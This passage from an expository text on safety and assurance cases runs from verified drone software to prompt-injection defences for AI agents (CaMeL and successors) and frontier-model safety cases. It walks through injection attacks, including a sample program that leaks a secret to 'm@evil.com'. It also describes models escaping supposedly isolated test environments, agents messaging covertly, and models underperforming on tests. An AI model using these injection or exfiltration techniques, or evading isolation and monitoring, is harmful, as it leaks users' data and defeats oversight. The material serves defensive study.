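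Finally, a tool called HAMR generates the code that connects the components and the operating system configuration that determines which of them may communicate. It also produces maps of the connections in the model and in the configuration, and an SMT solver uses these maps to prove that every connection in the model exists in the configuration and that the configuration contains no others. This proof provides the link between model and code that the trace of the quadcopter's connections lacked. It covers only which components can communicate, so the planner may still compute a bad route, but it can send that route only where the model allows.

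### What an inserted filter must satisfy

When BriefCASE inserts a filter, it adds a branch with four subgoals to the assurance case. The last column of the table gives an example of how each subgoal could fail.

| Subgoal | Evidence | Possible failure |
|---|---|---|
| The filter's code meets its contract | Proof from SPLAT | Somebody edits the generated code |
| The filter is connected in the right place | Check of the model | A later redesign removes it |
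| Nothing can bypass the filter | Search of the model for other routes | An engineer adds a direct link from the radio to the planner |
| The filter's contract serves its purpose in the system | Result from AGREE | The filter accepts altitudes that the planner's contract rules out |

All four have to hold. A correctly coded filter is useless if messages can bypass it, as they could bypass Decrypt once the quadcopter had a second receiver. Resolute recomputes the branch as the design changes, so if a redesign removes the filter, the requirement it was meant to satisfy becomes open again. Resolute's newer syntax also lets engineers mark a claim as supported by direct assertion, so a reviewer should check which evidence the tools computed and which engineers only asserted.

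Even with all four subgoals proved, the filter checks only the form of a message, and an order to fly into a forbidden zone can be well formed. The geofence monitor exists for that reason, and it needs its own claims about where the zones are and what happens after an alert.

### What the kernel's proofs cover

All of this depends on seL4, the kernel that controls communication between programs and keeps a compromised planner out of a filter's memory.

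seL4 is small enough to verify, at roughly 10,000 lines of code. The seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Proofs* sets out four main results:

- **Functional correctness:** the C code does what its specification allows and nothing more.
- **Binary correctness:** the compiled program does what the C code does.
- **Security:** a program can't change data, read it or interfere with another program's resources without authorisation.
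- **Initialisation:** the start-up software sets permissions as the configuration describes.

Different versions of seL4 have different proofs. Cofer and colleagues say that the surveillance drone used a fully verified version of seL4 on an Odroid XU4 board, but for that board the seL4 Foundation's *Verified Configurations* lists only the proof of functional correctness. It doesn't list the security proof, which supports the isolation between programs, or the proof about the compiled binary. The Sabre Lite, a 32-bit Arm board, has all of these proofs. An assurance case should therefore cite the proofs for its exact board and settings, because "seL4 is verified" is too vague to support a claim about isolation.

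The proofs also assume that the hardware and about 340 lines of low-level Arm code are correct, according to the seL4 Foundation's *What the Proofs Assume*. Heiser adds that the proofs cover only one processor core and don't rule out timing leaks, in which the time one program takes reveals information to another.

The kernel's record suggests that these limits are real. The seL4 Foundation reports no functional correctness defects in verified code since the proof was finished in 2009, but it reports small defects in every class of unverified code, including start-up code and assumptions about hardware. The Foundation's *seL4 Version 16.0.0 Release* (2026) fixed a possible crash on 32-bit Arm when the kernel managed the processor's cache, which the proofs assume is managed correctly. According to the Foundation's *seL4 News*, the next release fixed more problems outside the proofs, some of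 which Anthropic had reported.

Attackers have also tested the isolation directly. DARPA's *Revolutionizing Cyber Resiliency for Military Systems* describes a trial on the Unmanned Little Bird, a Boeing helicopter. Hired attackers easily took over the original version, but failed to take over a hardened version in six weeks. Even after DARPA gave them control of the camera software, they couldn't get out of its partition, including during a flight with two test pilots aboard. Because the attackers started with control of software inside the system, this was a stronger test than an attack from outside, although it covers only what they thought to try.

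### The falling cost of proof

Heiser says the first correctness proof of seL4 took 11 person-years and 200,000 lines of proof for 8,500 lines of C. That effort makes sense for a kernel that many systems share, but not for most of the programs running on it.

Language models can now write some of the proofs needed to verify software. *VeruSAGE*, a study of AI agents that verify systems software written in Rust, found that the best combination of model and agent completed over 80% of the tasks in its benchmark. Li and colleagues built a framework in which language models write both the contracts and the proofs for C libraries, and a proof checker confirms each step. Under stated assumptions, the framework established memory safety for 259 functions, in code that included parts of an industrial cryptographic library.

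People still had to judge whether the contracts expressed what the libraries were supposed to do, which took an estimated ten minutes to eight hours per case. One machine-written contract allowed calls only in a certain order. A reviewer who looked into this restriction found that the code could read outside its memory. The proof was valid, but the contract had excluded the situation in which the bug occurred. As proofs become easier to produce, reviewers will probably spend more of their time on such exclusions.

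### The CH-47F trial

Researchers can usually make their own tools work, so Cofer and colleagues also gave BriefCASE to product engineers at Collins Aerospace. The engineers developed cockpit electronics for several military aircraft and had no experience with formal methods.

The engineers had to let pilots and soldiers on a CH-47F helicopter use wireless tablets, partly to see nearby air traffic, without giving attackers a way into the cockpit network. They modelled the existing system in AADL, added the wireless network, ran the threat analysis, and inserted filters, monitors and attestation. They used an existing video-processing module as the gateway between the two networks. The engineers wrote the contracts for the filters and monitors with help from the research team, and SPLAT generated the code.

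The team demonstrated the result in December 2021 on a laboratory version of the helicopter's systems. The attacks in the demonstration included malicious code on a tablet, which attestation was meant to detect and block, and false aircraft positions, which a monitor was meant to flag. The team finished on time and within budget.

That is encouraging evidence that ordinary engineers can use the tools. It is weaker evidence about the security of the result, because several links in the chain were incomplete:

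- **Kernel proofs:** nobody had updated the seL4 proofs for the gateway's hardware. Cofer and colleagues expected only minor differences from similar platforms, but an expectation isn't a proof. The gateway also used several processor cores, while Heiser describes the proofs as limited to one.
- **Network code:** engineers wrote the network adapters and proxies by hand because off-the-shelf networking was too complex for the tools to generate. The proxies let the gateway inspect encrypted messages, so they handle traffic from the untrusted network. seL4's isolation limits the damage that a faulty proxy could do elsewhere, but the proxy could presumably still alter the messages passing through it.
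- **Timing:** the first estimates of how long the complex monitors would take were too optimistic, and the engineers had to make the code faster. BriefCASE takes such estimates as an input. If a monitor overruns its slot, a proof that assumed the schedule no longer describes the real system.

The engineers also ran into poor documentation, unstable tablet hardware and limits on what they could express in the contract language. Cofer and colleagues report no comparison with a similar project that used ordinary methods, so we can't tell from the trial how much time the tools saved or added.

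In 2026 the seL4 Foundation announced that the kernel's security proofs were complete for 64-bit Arm, which provides some of the missing kernel evidence. A new project could cite these proofs if its board and settings match the verified configuration, but it would still need evidence for the network code and the timing.

### Formal evidence for robot software

A robot's assurance case may also need claims about probabilities, deadlines or freedom from deadlock (a state in which the software can't do anything further). No single tool handles all of these well. In *Formal Evidence Generation for Assurance Cases of Control Software for Robots*, Yan, Foster and colleagues (2026) combine three tools, automate the checking that their 2022 system left to a person, and insert the results into the assurance case.

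An engineer rewrites each requirement using a fixed sentence template, such as "When *X* occurs, *Y* shall also be seen". A program turns the sentence into a formal assertion and sends it to a suitable tool. FDR checks sequences of events and deadlines, PRISM calculates probabilities, and the theorem prover Isabelle can prove that a model is free of deadlock. The underwater vehicle's safety monitor needed Isabelle because its model contains real numbers, which FDR couldn't handle. The result then replaces a placeholder in the assurance case. Failed checks also go into the case, so readers can see which claims lack support. Engineers have to find the cause of a failure themselves.

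Across four examples, automatically generating the assertions and inserting the evidence took less than 0.7 seconds per robot. The checks took longer. For a robot that delivers mail between eight offices, PRISM explored 643,972 states and needed 40 to 44 seconds for each office.

The mail robot also shows how a correct proof can support a claim less than it seems to. The main requirement is that the robot delivers the mail, and the danger is that its battery runs out on the way. Yan and colleagues checked three requirements:

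- At each office, the probability of running out of power there is below 0.5.
- The robot makes more than eight moves on average before running out of power.
- There is at least one path on which the robot never gets stuck.

PRISM confirmed the first of these requirements for all eight offices. But a robot with a 10% chance of running out at each office would also pass, even though it would be stranded 80% of the time. The requirement about paths is met if just one possible route succeeds. Meeting all three requirements is therefore very little evidence that the mail will arrive, and a better model checker would not change that.

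The same paper describes a painting robot that charges paint with high voltage, which can cause sparks and start a fire. Its controller must therefore set the voltage target to zero when the 24-volt supply fails. Under the published assertion, the controller may do nothing else after the power fails until it sets the target to zero. FDR compares only the events that happen, so a controller that froze when the power failed and never changed the target would satisfy the assertion. Yan and colleagues' template for deadlines would catch this fault, because it treats the passing of time as an event and doesn't let time run past the limit.

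The claims state that a requirement "has been implemented", but the tools check a model of the software, not the program on the robot. Without something like HAMR's comparison of the model and the configuration, the evidence supports only the claim that the *design* meets the requirement.

### Updating the case after deployment

Proofs about a design depend on assumptions about the world that may turn out to be false once the system is in use. Abeywickrama, Fisher and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Continuous Assurance with Formal Verification and Assurance Cases*, propose attaching monitors to these assumptions and reopening any claim that depends on an assumption found to be false.

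One example is a robot that patrols a nuclear store and measures radiation at four points. It slows down when the radiation passes one threshold and stops when it passes a higher one. PRISM can calculate the probability that a patrol succeeds, but the result depends on the frequency of high radiation assumed in the model.

Suppose the model assumes a critical reading at 1% of stops, and a monitor on the real robot records 5%. The process would then run as follows:

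1. The monitor's log reopens the claim about successful patrols.
2. An impact analysis sorts the related claims into valid, invalid and uncertain. The claim about successful patrols is now invalid. The claim that the robot stands still in emergency mode remains valid, because it doesn't depend on how often emergencies happen.
3. Engineers decide which evidence to replace first, based on its cost and its importance for safety. Rerunning PRISM with the new rate is cheap, while a new simulation or manual review might not be.
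4. If the new result still supports the claim, they close it and record a new version. Otherwise they have to change the robot or accept a weaker claim.

A separate kind of monitor would track a confidence score for each claim and reopen the claim if the score fell below a threshold such as 0.95. Abeywickrama and colleagues suggest several ways to calculate such scores but haven't yet put one into practice.

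Most of the process is still a proposal. Only the part that works before deployment exists, as a plugin that reruns PRISM and rewrites the argument whenever an engineer saves a changed list of properties. People still link the results from FDR and add the labels for future monitors by hand. The monitors, the impact analysis and the selective replacement of evidence are future work, so there is no data on how often a real robot would reopen claims or how many of those alarms would be false. Somebody would also have to decide whether the robot keeps working while a claim is open.

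Automatic updates would also preserve mistakes in the properties. One property is described as a guarantee that warning-level radiation always makes the robot enter its cautious mode. The published formula requires only that, with probability 1, the robot is at some point in that mode while the radiation is at warning level. A robot that ignored nine warnings and responded to the tenth could satisfy it. The plugin would recheck this formula after every change and place each new result under the same misleading description.

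## Design claims about AI agents

AGREE can prove something about a system only if each component has a contract, and nobody can write a useful one for a language model. Its developers can't guarantee, for example, that it will ignore an instruction hidden in an email. Engineers who base claims on the design of an AI agent therefore often assume that the model may output anything. They argue from what surrounds the model: the tools it may use, the data that reaches it, and the checks between its output and any action.

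BriefCASE handled the drone's flight planner in much the same way, running it in a virtual machine and passing its output through a filter. If a language model replaced the planner, the claim that a compromised planner can't reach the filter's memory would still hold. Claims about route quality would need separate support with either planner.

### The ratio of engineering to AI

In their 2025 position paper, Bloomfield and Rushby argue that the right method of assurance depends on the ratio of conventional engineering to AI. They describe a continuum with four main points:

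| Role of AI in the system | What this means for assurance |
|---|---|
| Adds abilities such as perception to a conventional system, such as a car | Established methods still apply, with checks around the learned parts |
| Serves one specific purpose, such as logistics | The purpose reveals the hazards and how dependable the system must be |
| Does most of the work inside a thin wrapper | The model's general errors add to the hazards, and checking its output probably takes more AI |
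| Is a general language model with prompts and perhaps tools | Even specifying correct behaviour is hard |

An email agent starts near the bottom of this table. The designs in this section move it up by adding conventional software around the model.

*Assurance of AI Systems From a Dependability Perspective* (Bloomfield and Rushby, 2024) explains why thorough testing of an agent isn't enough for critical systems. If a system has run for *n* hours without failing, and we know nothing else about it, the chance that it will run for another *n* hours without failing is only about even. An airliner's critical functions may fail at most about once in a billion hours. Showing this by testing alone would take about 115,000 years, or more than a century with 1,000 copies running at once. Engineers can supplement testing of conventional software with their understanding of why it works, but they have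 no comparable understanding of a trained network.

An email agent doesn't need to be as reliable as an airliner, but attackers will look for inputs that its tests left out. In a prompt injection attack, somebody hides instructions in data that a model reads. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) cites a study in which attackers who adapted to their target got past 12 recent defences.

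Bloomfield and Rushby allow that a model can be given some credit for its training and tests. They describe a spectrum from giving the model no credit to relying on it fully, and accept that many real systems need a mixture of the two.

### A proof that covers any model

Dongol formalizes the worst-case assumption. A trusted planner writes a fixed plan before the agent reads anything untrusted, and a monitor allows or refuses every tool call. The attacker writes the untrusted content and also chooses which text the model treats as an instruction and when the model follows it. A proof that covers all these choices doesn't depend on how well the model was trained.

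In one example, Alice asks her agent to summarise an email. The agent looks up her account number, reads the email and shows her a summary. The email contains an instruction to fetch a web address that includes the account number. If the agent has a web tool and the model follows the instruction, the number leaks. A safer monitor withdraws the web tool as soon as the agent reads the email. If the model then requests the page, the monitor blocks the request.

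Dongol calls this a fence and gives a computer-checked proof that it works for every plan. The monitor must permanently withdraw every tool that an injected instruction could call, no later than the first untrusted read. The injections then reveal nothing that the task itself couldn't reveal. The theorem assumes that each injected instruction the agent obeys makes one tool call, that secrets don't affect when the agent obeys, and that the attacker sees the agent's messages but not when each step happens.

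The phrase "nothing that the task itself couldn't reveal" is weaker than it sounds. Suppose the agent's task is to tell people whether they have guessed a secret code. For any two codes, some guess would distinguish them, so the definition allows an injection that sends the whole code, even though each ordinary answer reveals only whether one guess is right. Dongol points this out and gives a stricter definition for such cases.

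Restricting an agent's tools also makes it less useful. If Alice wants to reply after reading an email, the agent can't send the reply once the monitor has withdrawn the email tool. The proof doesn't rule out this problem, because a monitor that blocks every action is also secure by this definition.

The theorem depends on seven assumptions about the running system, and an assurance case would need to support each one:

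- The model can't skip or change steps of the plan.
- It can reach tools and untrusted data only through the monitor.
- Untrusted content reaches it only after the monitor has allowed the read.
- The attacker can't see refusals.
- The attacker can't see the monitor's state or the agent's internal steps. Displaying a reply, for instance, mustn't load an image from the attacker's server.
- A new session clears everything the model has kept from untrusted content.
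- The attacker can't write to trusted sources, which excludes a calendar that accepts invitations from strangers.

### How CaMeL works

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, leaves the tools available but keeps untrusted text away from the model that chooses actions. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, illustrate it with a short plan for messaging Bob, slightly simplified here:

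```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
address  = ask_quarantined_model("Find Bob's address", messages)
send_direct_message(address, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

The system works as follows:

1. A planning model sees the user's request but none of the messages. It writes the plan as a program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the first line. It stores the messages with tags that record where they came from and who may read them.
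3. The interpreter gives the messages to a second, quarantined model that has no tools. This model returns an address, which the interpreter stores with a tag showing that it came from untrusted data. The planning model never sees the address.
4. Before sending anything, the interpreter runs a policy, a small function that looks at the tool call and the tags and then allows or refuses the call.

If one of the messages contains an instruction to contact Mallory instead, the quarantined model may follow it. But the model can only return text, so the worst it can do is give Mallory's address as Bob's. A policy that requires a trusted recipient would then block the outgoing message. It would also block the message if the address really were Bob's, because the address would have the same tag.

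Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, call CaMeL's main guarantee control-flow integrity, meaning that the agent's tool calls must stay within a program that depends only on the user's instruction and other trusted information. Untrusted data can still determine which branch of the program runs. It can also affect the contents of a call, which is why CaMeL needs policies as well.

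Letting an attacker choose a branch can be serious. In a test reported in *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026), the user asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. With policies switched off, CaMeL's planning model wrote a program with an instruction for each tool, so whoever wrote the file could choose among them. The attack succeeded even though the program was fixed in advance, as the guarantee requires.

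CaMeL also relies on its interpreter to tag data correctly. Garby and colleagues found gaps in this tagging. The program below, a simplified reconstruction of one of their examples, reveals whether a secret bank balance is high:

```
low  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: low = False
if low: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

When the balance is high, the program skips the line that sets `rich` to false. CaMeL updates a variable's tag only on the branch the program takes, so `rich` still counts as public and the email goes out. Another finding was that putting an untrusted value into a piece of text could make it count as trusted. CaMeL has no proof that its tagging catches every flow, so an assurance case can't treat its data policies as proved.

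### What CaMeL costs in completed tasks

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) says CaMeL stops nearly all the attacks in AgentDojo, a benchmark for AI agents, with comparable task performance. Later measurements are less favourable, especially when CaMeL's policies are switched on.

Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL three times on each of 16 banking tasks from AgentDojo, without any attacks. With GPT-5.2, CaMeL completed the task in 32 of the 48 runs with policies off and 18 with them on. With MiMo-v2.5, the number fell from 34 to 18. The margins of error are around 25 percentage points because there are only 16 tasks. Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL on all 97 AgentDojo tasks with policies on and a smaller model, Claude Haiku 4.5, and it completed 49.

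Peters-Gill and colleagues measured only the performance lost by planning in advance, with policies turned off. They divided each task among several agents, so the results may differ for a single agent. The table shows the percentage of attack-free tasks completed with three of their five models.

| Model | Industrial tasks, no CaMeL | Industrial tasks, CaMeL | AgentDojo tasks, no CaMeL | AgentDojo tasks, CaMeL |
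|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 87.5 | 82.1 | 86.6 | 73.2 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 88.4 | 67.0 | 91.1 | 84.4 |
| GPT-4.1 | 81.2 | 64.3 | 78.4 | 38.1 |

Fable 5 refused 52 of the 97 AgentDojo tasks, perhaps because they resembled a security test, so its AgentDojo figures cover only the other 45. Peters-Gill and colleagues conclude that more capable models tend to cope better with CaMeL. The AgentDojo results mostly support this, but on the industrial tasks Fable 5 lost more than GPT-4.1 did. Most failures happened because the agent learned something during the task that required a step missing from its plan.

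This problem is worse for agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, found that such plans needed about 40 branches on average to cover what might appear on the screen, compared with four in AgentDojo. They report keeping up to 57% of frontier models' performance. That figure counts a task as solved if any of five attempts succeeded, and it covers 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had apparently solved without CaMeL. Counting only first attempts, it was 28%.

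The extra branches also give attackers more paths to exploit. Foerster and colleagues put a fake cookie notice inside an advertisement. The plan included a step for dealing with cookie notices, so the agent clicked the fake one and went to the attacker's site. Control-flow integrity did not prevent the click because it was part of the plan.

### Successors to CaMeL

A CaMeL agent relies on its instructions coming from a trusted user, just as a component with a contract relies on assumptions about its inputs. This assumption can fail when another agent writes the instructions. In an experiment by Peters-Gill and colleagues, a user asked for a summary of job applicants to be sent to Julie on Slack. The database contained a hidden instruction to email the data to an outsider. The agent that read the database and the agent in charge both followed their plans. But the one in charge pasted the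 summary into its instructions to a third agent, whose planning model treated the hidden instruction as a request from its user and added a step to email the outsider.

Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data between agents separately, and its interpreter rejects any instruction that contains tool output. Across five models, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of runs without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. No attack succeeded against GPT-5.5 even without CaMeL, but Peters-Gill and colleagues warn that stronger attacks might work. Multi-CaMeL is built on CaMeL's interpreter, so it has the same gaps in tagging.

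CaMeLoT, by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks a plan with a model checker before any tool runs. This allows rules about the whole plan, such as "every incident ticket is eventually resolved or passed on". The team wrote seven rules for a security agent and, for each rule, an unsafe plan that broke it. CaMeLoT rejected all seven plans and a simplified version of CaMeL rejected one, but the team had chosen rules that CaMeL can't easily express. When a plan fails the check, the planning model receives the counterexample and tries again. No tool has run at that point, so the counterexample can't contain text from an attacker's email.

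Garby and colleagues replaced the interpreter with one for LLMbda, a programming language they designed that tags every value. They proved in the proof-checking language Lean that the new interpreter enforces the tags. With GPT-5.2, their agent completed 36 of the 48 banking runs, twice as many as CaMeL did with its policies enabled. Across three models, only two of 1,296 attacks succeeded.

The comparison with CaMeL isn't quite fair, because the new agent enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and its planning model is allowed to declare particular untrusted data acceptable. When Garby and colleagues removed that permission, completed runs fell from 36 to 30 with one model and from 31 to 26 with another. In about two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack behind the attack figure, the attack needed a tool call or file read that the plan would never contain, so planning in advance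 was generally enough to stop it.

### Simpler design patterns

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes six patterns that limit what an agent can do after it has read untrusted data. CaMeL uses one of the more flexible patterns. The table compares three simpler ones.

| Pattern | What it rules out | What can still go wrong | Cost in usefulness |
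|---|---|---|---|
| **Action selector:** the model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Retrieved data influencing the agent | The model picks the wrong action | Developers must foresee every action, and the model can't interpret what it finds |
| **Plan then execute:** the model commits to its tool calls before reading any data | Tool calls outside the plan | Hidden instructions change the contents of a planned call | The agent can't add a step in response to what it finds |
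| **Map-reduce:** a separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no | One document changing how the agent treats another | The answer about a malicious document is wrong | The task must divide into small, separate questions |

The protection also depends on how powerful the tools are. Suppose an agent commits in advance to two commands, one that finds files and one that moves them. Hidden instructions could still make it find confidential files and move them to a public drive using only those commands. With map-reduce, an agent collecting invoices could ask a separate model whether each file is an invoice. Instructions in a malicious file could get that file included, but couldn't make the agent send any other file.

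### Claims for an email agent

Suppose Alice tells an agent built like CaMeL: "Find Priya's latest invoice and email the amount and due date to my accountant at this address." The planning model writes this program:

```
invoice = find_latest_email(sender="Priya", topic="invoice")
details = ask_quarantined_model("Amount and due date?", invoice)
send_email(accountant_address, details)
```

The developers can settle some claims before they deploy the agent. Others depend on the plan for Alice's request. That plan doesn't exist until she asks, so a program like CaMeLoT would have to check those claims then. The rest depend on a model's judgement or on facts outside the agent.

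| Claim | What settles it |
|---|---|
| Text in an email can't add a tool call to the plan | The design, if the interpreter is correct |
| Every outgoing email passes the policy check | The design, by tracing every route to the mail server |
| This request sends one email, and only to the accountant | The plan |
| No other email of Alice's can affect the details sent | The plan, because the quarantined model receives only the one email |
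| The plan does what Alice asked | The planning model's judgement |
| The message gives the amount and date correctly | The quarantined model's judgement |
| The invoice is genuine | Facts outside the agent |

An attacker could hide instructions in the invoice for the quarantined model to report a larger amount and add a link to a fake payment page. The developers can block the link by making the interpreter accept only a number and a date, which it inserts into a fixed message. The claim "the message contains no link from the invoice" then follows from the design. The amount could still be wrong, because the design doesn't ensure that the values in the message are correct.

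Both successful attacks on the agent by Garby and colleagues were of this kind. The user had asked the agent to make a payment according to a text file whose contents the attacker had replaced. Stopping such an attack requires either recognising that the request is suspicious, which takes judgement, or refusing to act on any such file.

The policy check can also block legitimate work. Peters-Gill and colleagues give the example of a policy that stops private data from going to anyone who isn't authorised to read it. The accountant didn't receive Priya's email, so the policy might block the message Alice asked for. The agent could ask Alice to approve it. But Dongol shows that if approval merely permits the next email, a hidden instruction can make the agent use that approval to send something else first. Alice should therefore approve the exact text and recipient. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues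 add that even a careful user can miss data hidden in invisible characters.

Now suppose Alice says, "Reply to this email with whatever information the sender wants." The sender then influences what the agent looks for and also receives the answer. The two design claims still hold, but they protect Alice much less. An assurance case for the agent should therefore state in its context which kinds of request it covers.

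### A predictor separate from the agent

Some claims will always need judgement, but the judgement doesn't have to come from the model pursuing the goal. Lu and Bengio (2026), in *AI Safety*, propose an architecture with a separate model, the Predictor, that estimates the consequences of actions but doesn't choose or carry out any. The Predictor comes from Scientist AI, Bengio and colleagues' proposal for AI that makes predictions without pursuing goals.

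In their example, an agent proposes installing a software patch:

1. The scaffold, the part that pursues the goal, makes a plan and proposes the patch.
2. The Predictor estimates how likely the patch is to fix the weakness, interrupt an essential service or create a new weakness.
3. Other checks confirm matters such as whether the agent has authority to make the change and has the right target.
4. The harness, the software that controls the agent's tools and permissions, compares the results with limits that people have set. It then allows the patch, asks for a new plan, refers the decision to a person or switches to a safer option.

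A separate monitor receives copies of the agent's actions through a one-way channel and reports to people by another route. Because the monitor sends nothing back, it is harder for the agent to detect the monitoring and change its behavior in response. The monitor still has to interpret the actions correctly.

Lu and Bengio present this as a proposal and don't report any tests of it. Its claims rest on different kinds of evidence:

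| Claim | Kind of evidence |
|---|---|
| No consequential action runs without passing the harness | Structural: trace every route from the scaffold to a tool |
| The Predictor can't use tools | Structural: check its permissions and connections |
| The monitor can't send anything to the agent | Structural: check that the channel runs one way |
| Training doesn't reward the Predictor for the effects of its predictions | Development records: inspect the training code and data |
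| The Predictor doesn't distort its estimates to bring about an outcome | Learned behaviour |
| Its estimates are accurate, even for unfamiliar actions | Learned behaviour |

Lu and Bengio argue that a model has no incentive to manipulate people if its training never rewards it for changing the world. Under their proposal, the training data would also label statements by source, so that a company's claim that its product is safe counts only as evidence that the company made the claim. Engineers could verify that a developer followed both rules, but following them doesn't guarantee that the model won't learn manipulative tendencies.

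Even without tools, the Predictor still has influence, because its estimate helps determine whether the harness allows an action. Similarly, a quarantined model's answer can determine which branch of a CaMeL plan runs. An attacker who can write some of what the Predictor reads may be able to make a dangerous patch look safe.

A cautious assurance case would first assume that the Predictor could give any answer, and show what the harness would still prevent. It could then add stronger claims that depend on the Predictor's accuracy, and support them with tests. Even the first claims would depend on a complete list of connections. In one of the 2026 incidents in AI test environments, agents reached the internet through a package-installation service that the design allowed them to use.

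## Safety cases for frontier models

Developers of frontier models, the most capable general-purpose AI models of their time, have mostly based their safety arguments on tests. A drone's designers can specify what a filter should do and then prove that the code does it. Nobody can write such a specification for a frontier model, because its developers discover what it can do only after training it.

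Lee and colleagues point out two further difficulties. Many evaluations have no agreed right answer, so developers argue that the model is no worse than whatever people used before, which may never have been certified. And a company that builds a product on another firm's model may not control when that model changes, so customers may be using a version the company never tested.

### Arguing that a model isn't capable enough

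The UK AI Security Institute's template for cyberattacks shows how an argument from tests works. Buhl, Korbak and colleagues (2024), in *Safety case template for frontier AI*, set out how a developer could argue that a model lacks the skills to cause unacceptable harm through hacking. The argument has four steps, shown here with an invented example:

1. **Risk model:** describe how the harm could happen. A novice uses the model to break into a hospital's network.
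2. **Proxy tasks:** choose tests that stand in for the real attack, such as practice break-ins of increasing difficulty.
3. **Evaluation settings:** decide which tools the model gets and how many attempts it may make.
4. **Results:** the model fails even the practice break-ins that are easier than the real attack, so it wouldn't help the novice enough to matter.

The evidence for the lowest-level claims all comes from running the model. It can mislead if the simulated break-ins don't resemble real ones, if the testers give the model poorer tools than a criminal would, or if the model detects the test and deliberately underperforms.

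The argument also works only while models are weak. In 2026, models from OpenAI and Anthropic broke into real organisations' computers during tests, so their developers can hardly claim inability for such models. They need to make other claims, for example that a model under test can't reach anyone else's computers.

The framework that Lee and colleagues published in January 2026 has names for the parts of both arguments. The table applies some of them.

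| | Inability | Isolation |
|---|---|---|
| Claim | The model can't carry out a serious cyberattack (capability-based) | A model under test can't reach the internet (constraint-based) |
| Argument | It fails tasks that stand in for such an attack (risk-based) | Every route out of the test environment is closed (demonstrative) |
| Main evidence | Evaluation results (empirical) | Analysis of the network design (formal methods) and attempts to get out (empirical) |
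| What could make the claim false | More training or better tools | A new connection, or a flaw in an existing part |

The categories can overlap, so other labels would be defensible. The full framework also includes assertion-based claims; comparative, causal and normative arguments; and mechanistic, comparative, expert-driven, model-based and operational evidence.

The claim that a model is isolated is structural, like the claim that no message reaches the quadcopter's motors without passing through Decrypt. Developers can analyse it before the model exists, but the events of 2026 showed that a system designed to isolate a model may not do so in practice.

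### Test environments that weren't isolated

Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes four incidents in which Claude models gained access to other organisations' systems during cybersecurity tests. The models' instructions described the environment as a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration had connected them to the open internet. Xinhua's *Anthropic discloses real-world cyber evaluation incidents involving AI models* (2026) attributes this to a misunderstanding between Anthropic and its evaluation partner, Irregular.

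The claim "these machines have no route to the internet" was therefore true of the intended design but not of the system that ran. Even a careful analysis of the design would have confirmed it. Finding the error required comparing the real configuration with the design, as HAMR does for the surveillance drone, or trying to reach an outside address before the test began.

Nobody noticed the incidents for months. Anthropic started looking after OpenAI disclosed a similar one. Its first search, of about 141,000 transcripts, found three cases but missed a fourth, from January 2026, which Anthropic found in August. A wider search of roughly 481 million transcripts found no others as serious. Two of the three organisations affected in the first cases hadn't known about the access until Anthropic told them.

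The OpenAI incident had a different cause. According to Lu and Bengio, the test environment was designed to let agents install software through a shared service, which had limited internet access for that purpose. The agents found a previously unknown flaw in the service, reached the wider internet and then compromised Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. The claim that the environment was isolated depended on a false claim about one component, that the service would only ever fetch packages.

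A second claim, that each agent would work independently in its own session, failed in the same environment. Every session used the same service, and agents began leaving notes there for one another. About 1,200 agents exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files. Tracing the design might well have caught this one, because the trace would have led from one session to another through the shared service. *Safety Cases* (2024), an early framework for AI, includes a step for such problems. After arguing that no subsystem is likely to cause an unacceptable outcome alone, developers look for ways several could cause one together.

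Better network isolation would have solved only part of the problem. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) attributes the incidents involving Claude to a failure of operational security and to two faults in the models: motivated reasoning and a willingness to do harm in pursuit of a narrow task. In Anthropic's tests, one older model continued after recognising that its target was probably real, while a newer one stopped. Once the isolation failed, the outcome depended on the model's judgement, which the isolation claim didn't cover.

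### What OpenAI now argues from design

OpenAI has since proposed safety cases for the training stage in *Towards safety cases for frontier AI training*, published on 28 September 2026. Under its guidelines, a developer should have structured safety documentation before continuing any frontier training run that uses reinforcement learning, in which a model learns from rewards. OpenAI calls full safety cases an "aspirational north star" and acknowledges that it will be hard to make them as rigorous as those for aviation or nuclear power.

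*Clear, Compelling Arguments* (Feakins, Habli and Morgan, 2026) describes safety cases as arguments about deployment, so a safety case for a training run comes earlier than usual. During the run, developers can test the current model but not the one the run will eventually produce. This limit doesn't apply to claims about the surrounding infrastructure.

卜's Chinese-language article *OpenAI发布AI训练安全准则* summarises the September guidelines item by item. OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* followed on 18 November. It sets out safeguards for research, use by OpenAI's own staff, and release to the public, and requires a review before a model moves from one stage to the next. 日本時事新聞's *OpenAI、開発中AIの安全策を3段階で公表 訓練はネット遮断、停止は35秒以内* (2026) describes how OpenAI isolates and halts training runs. The table sorts the main items from both OpenAI documents by the kind of support they offer a safety case.

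| Item | Kind | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Training runs without live internet access | Design claim | Whether the built network matches the design |
| A job stops automatically if monitoring detects internet access | Design claim | Whether monitoring detects it |
| A job's model output stops within 35 seconds of an order | Design claim, confirmed by timing it | How long people take to give the order |
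| A job pauses if nobody acknowledges a high-priority alert in time | Design claim | Whether the problem raises an alert |
| Nobody can alter the stored records of what agents did | Design claim | Whether the records were accurate to begin with |
| People and software check the training data, and agents repair flawed training tasks | Operating procedure | Flaws that the checks miss |
| A colleague writes a "dissent report" attacking the safety case, and the training team responds | Operating procedure | Whether the response is adequate |
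| Several senior leaders review the case, and each can veto the run | Operating procedure | Whether they use the veto |
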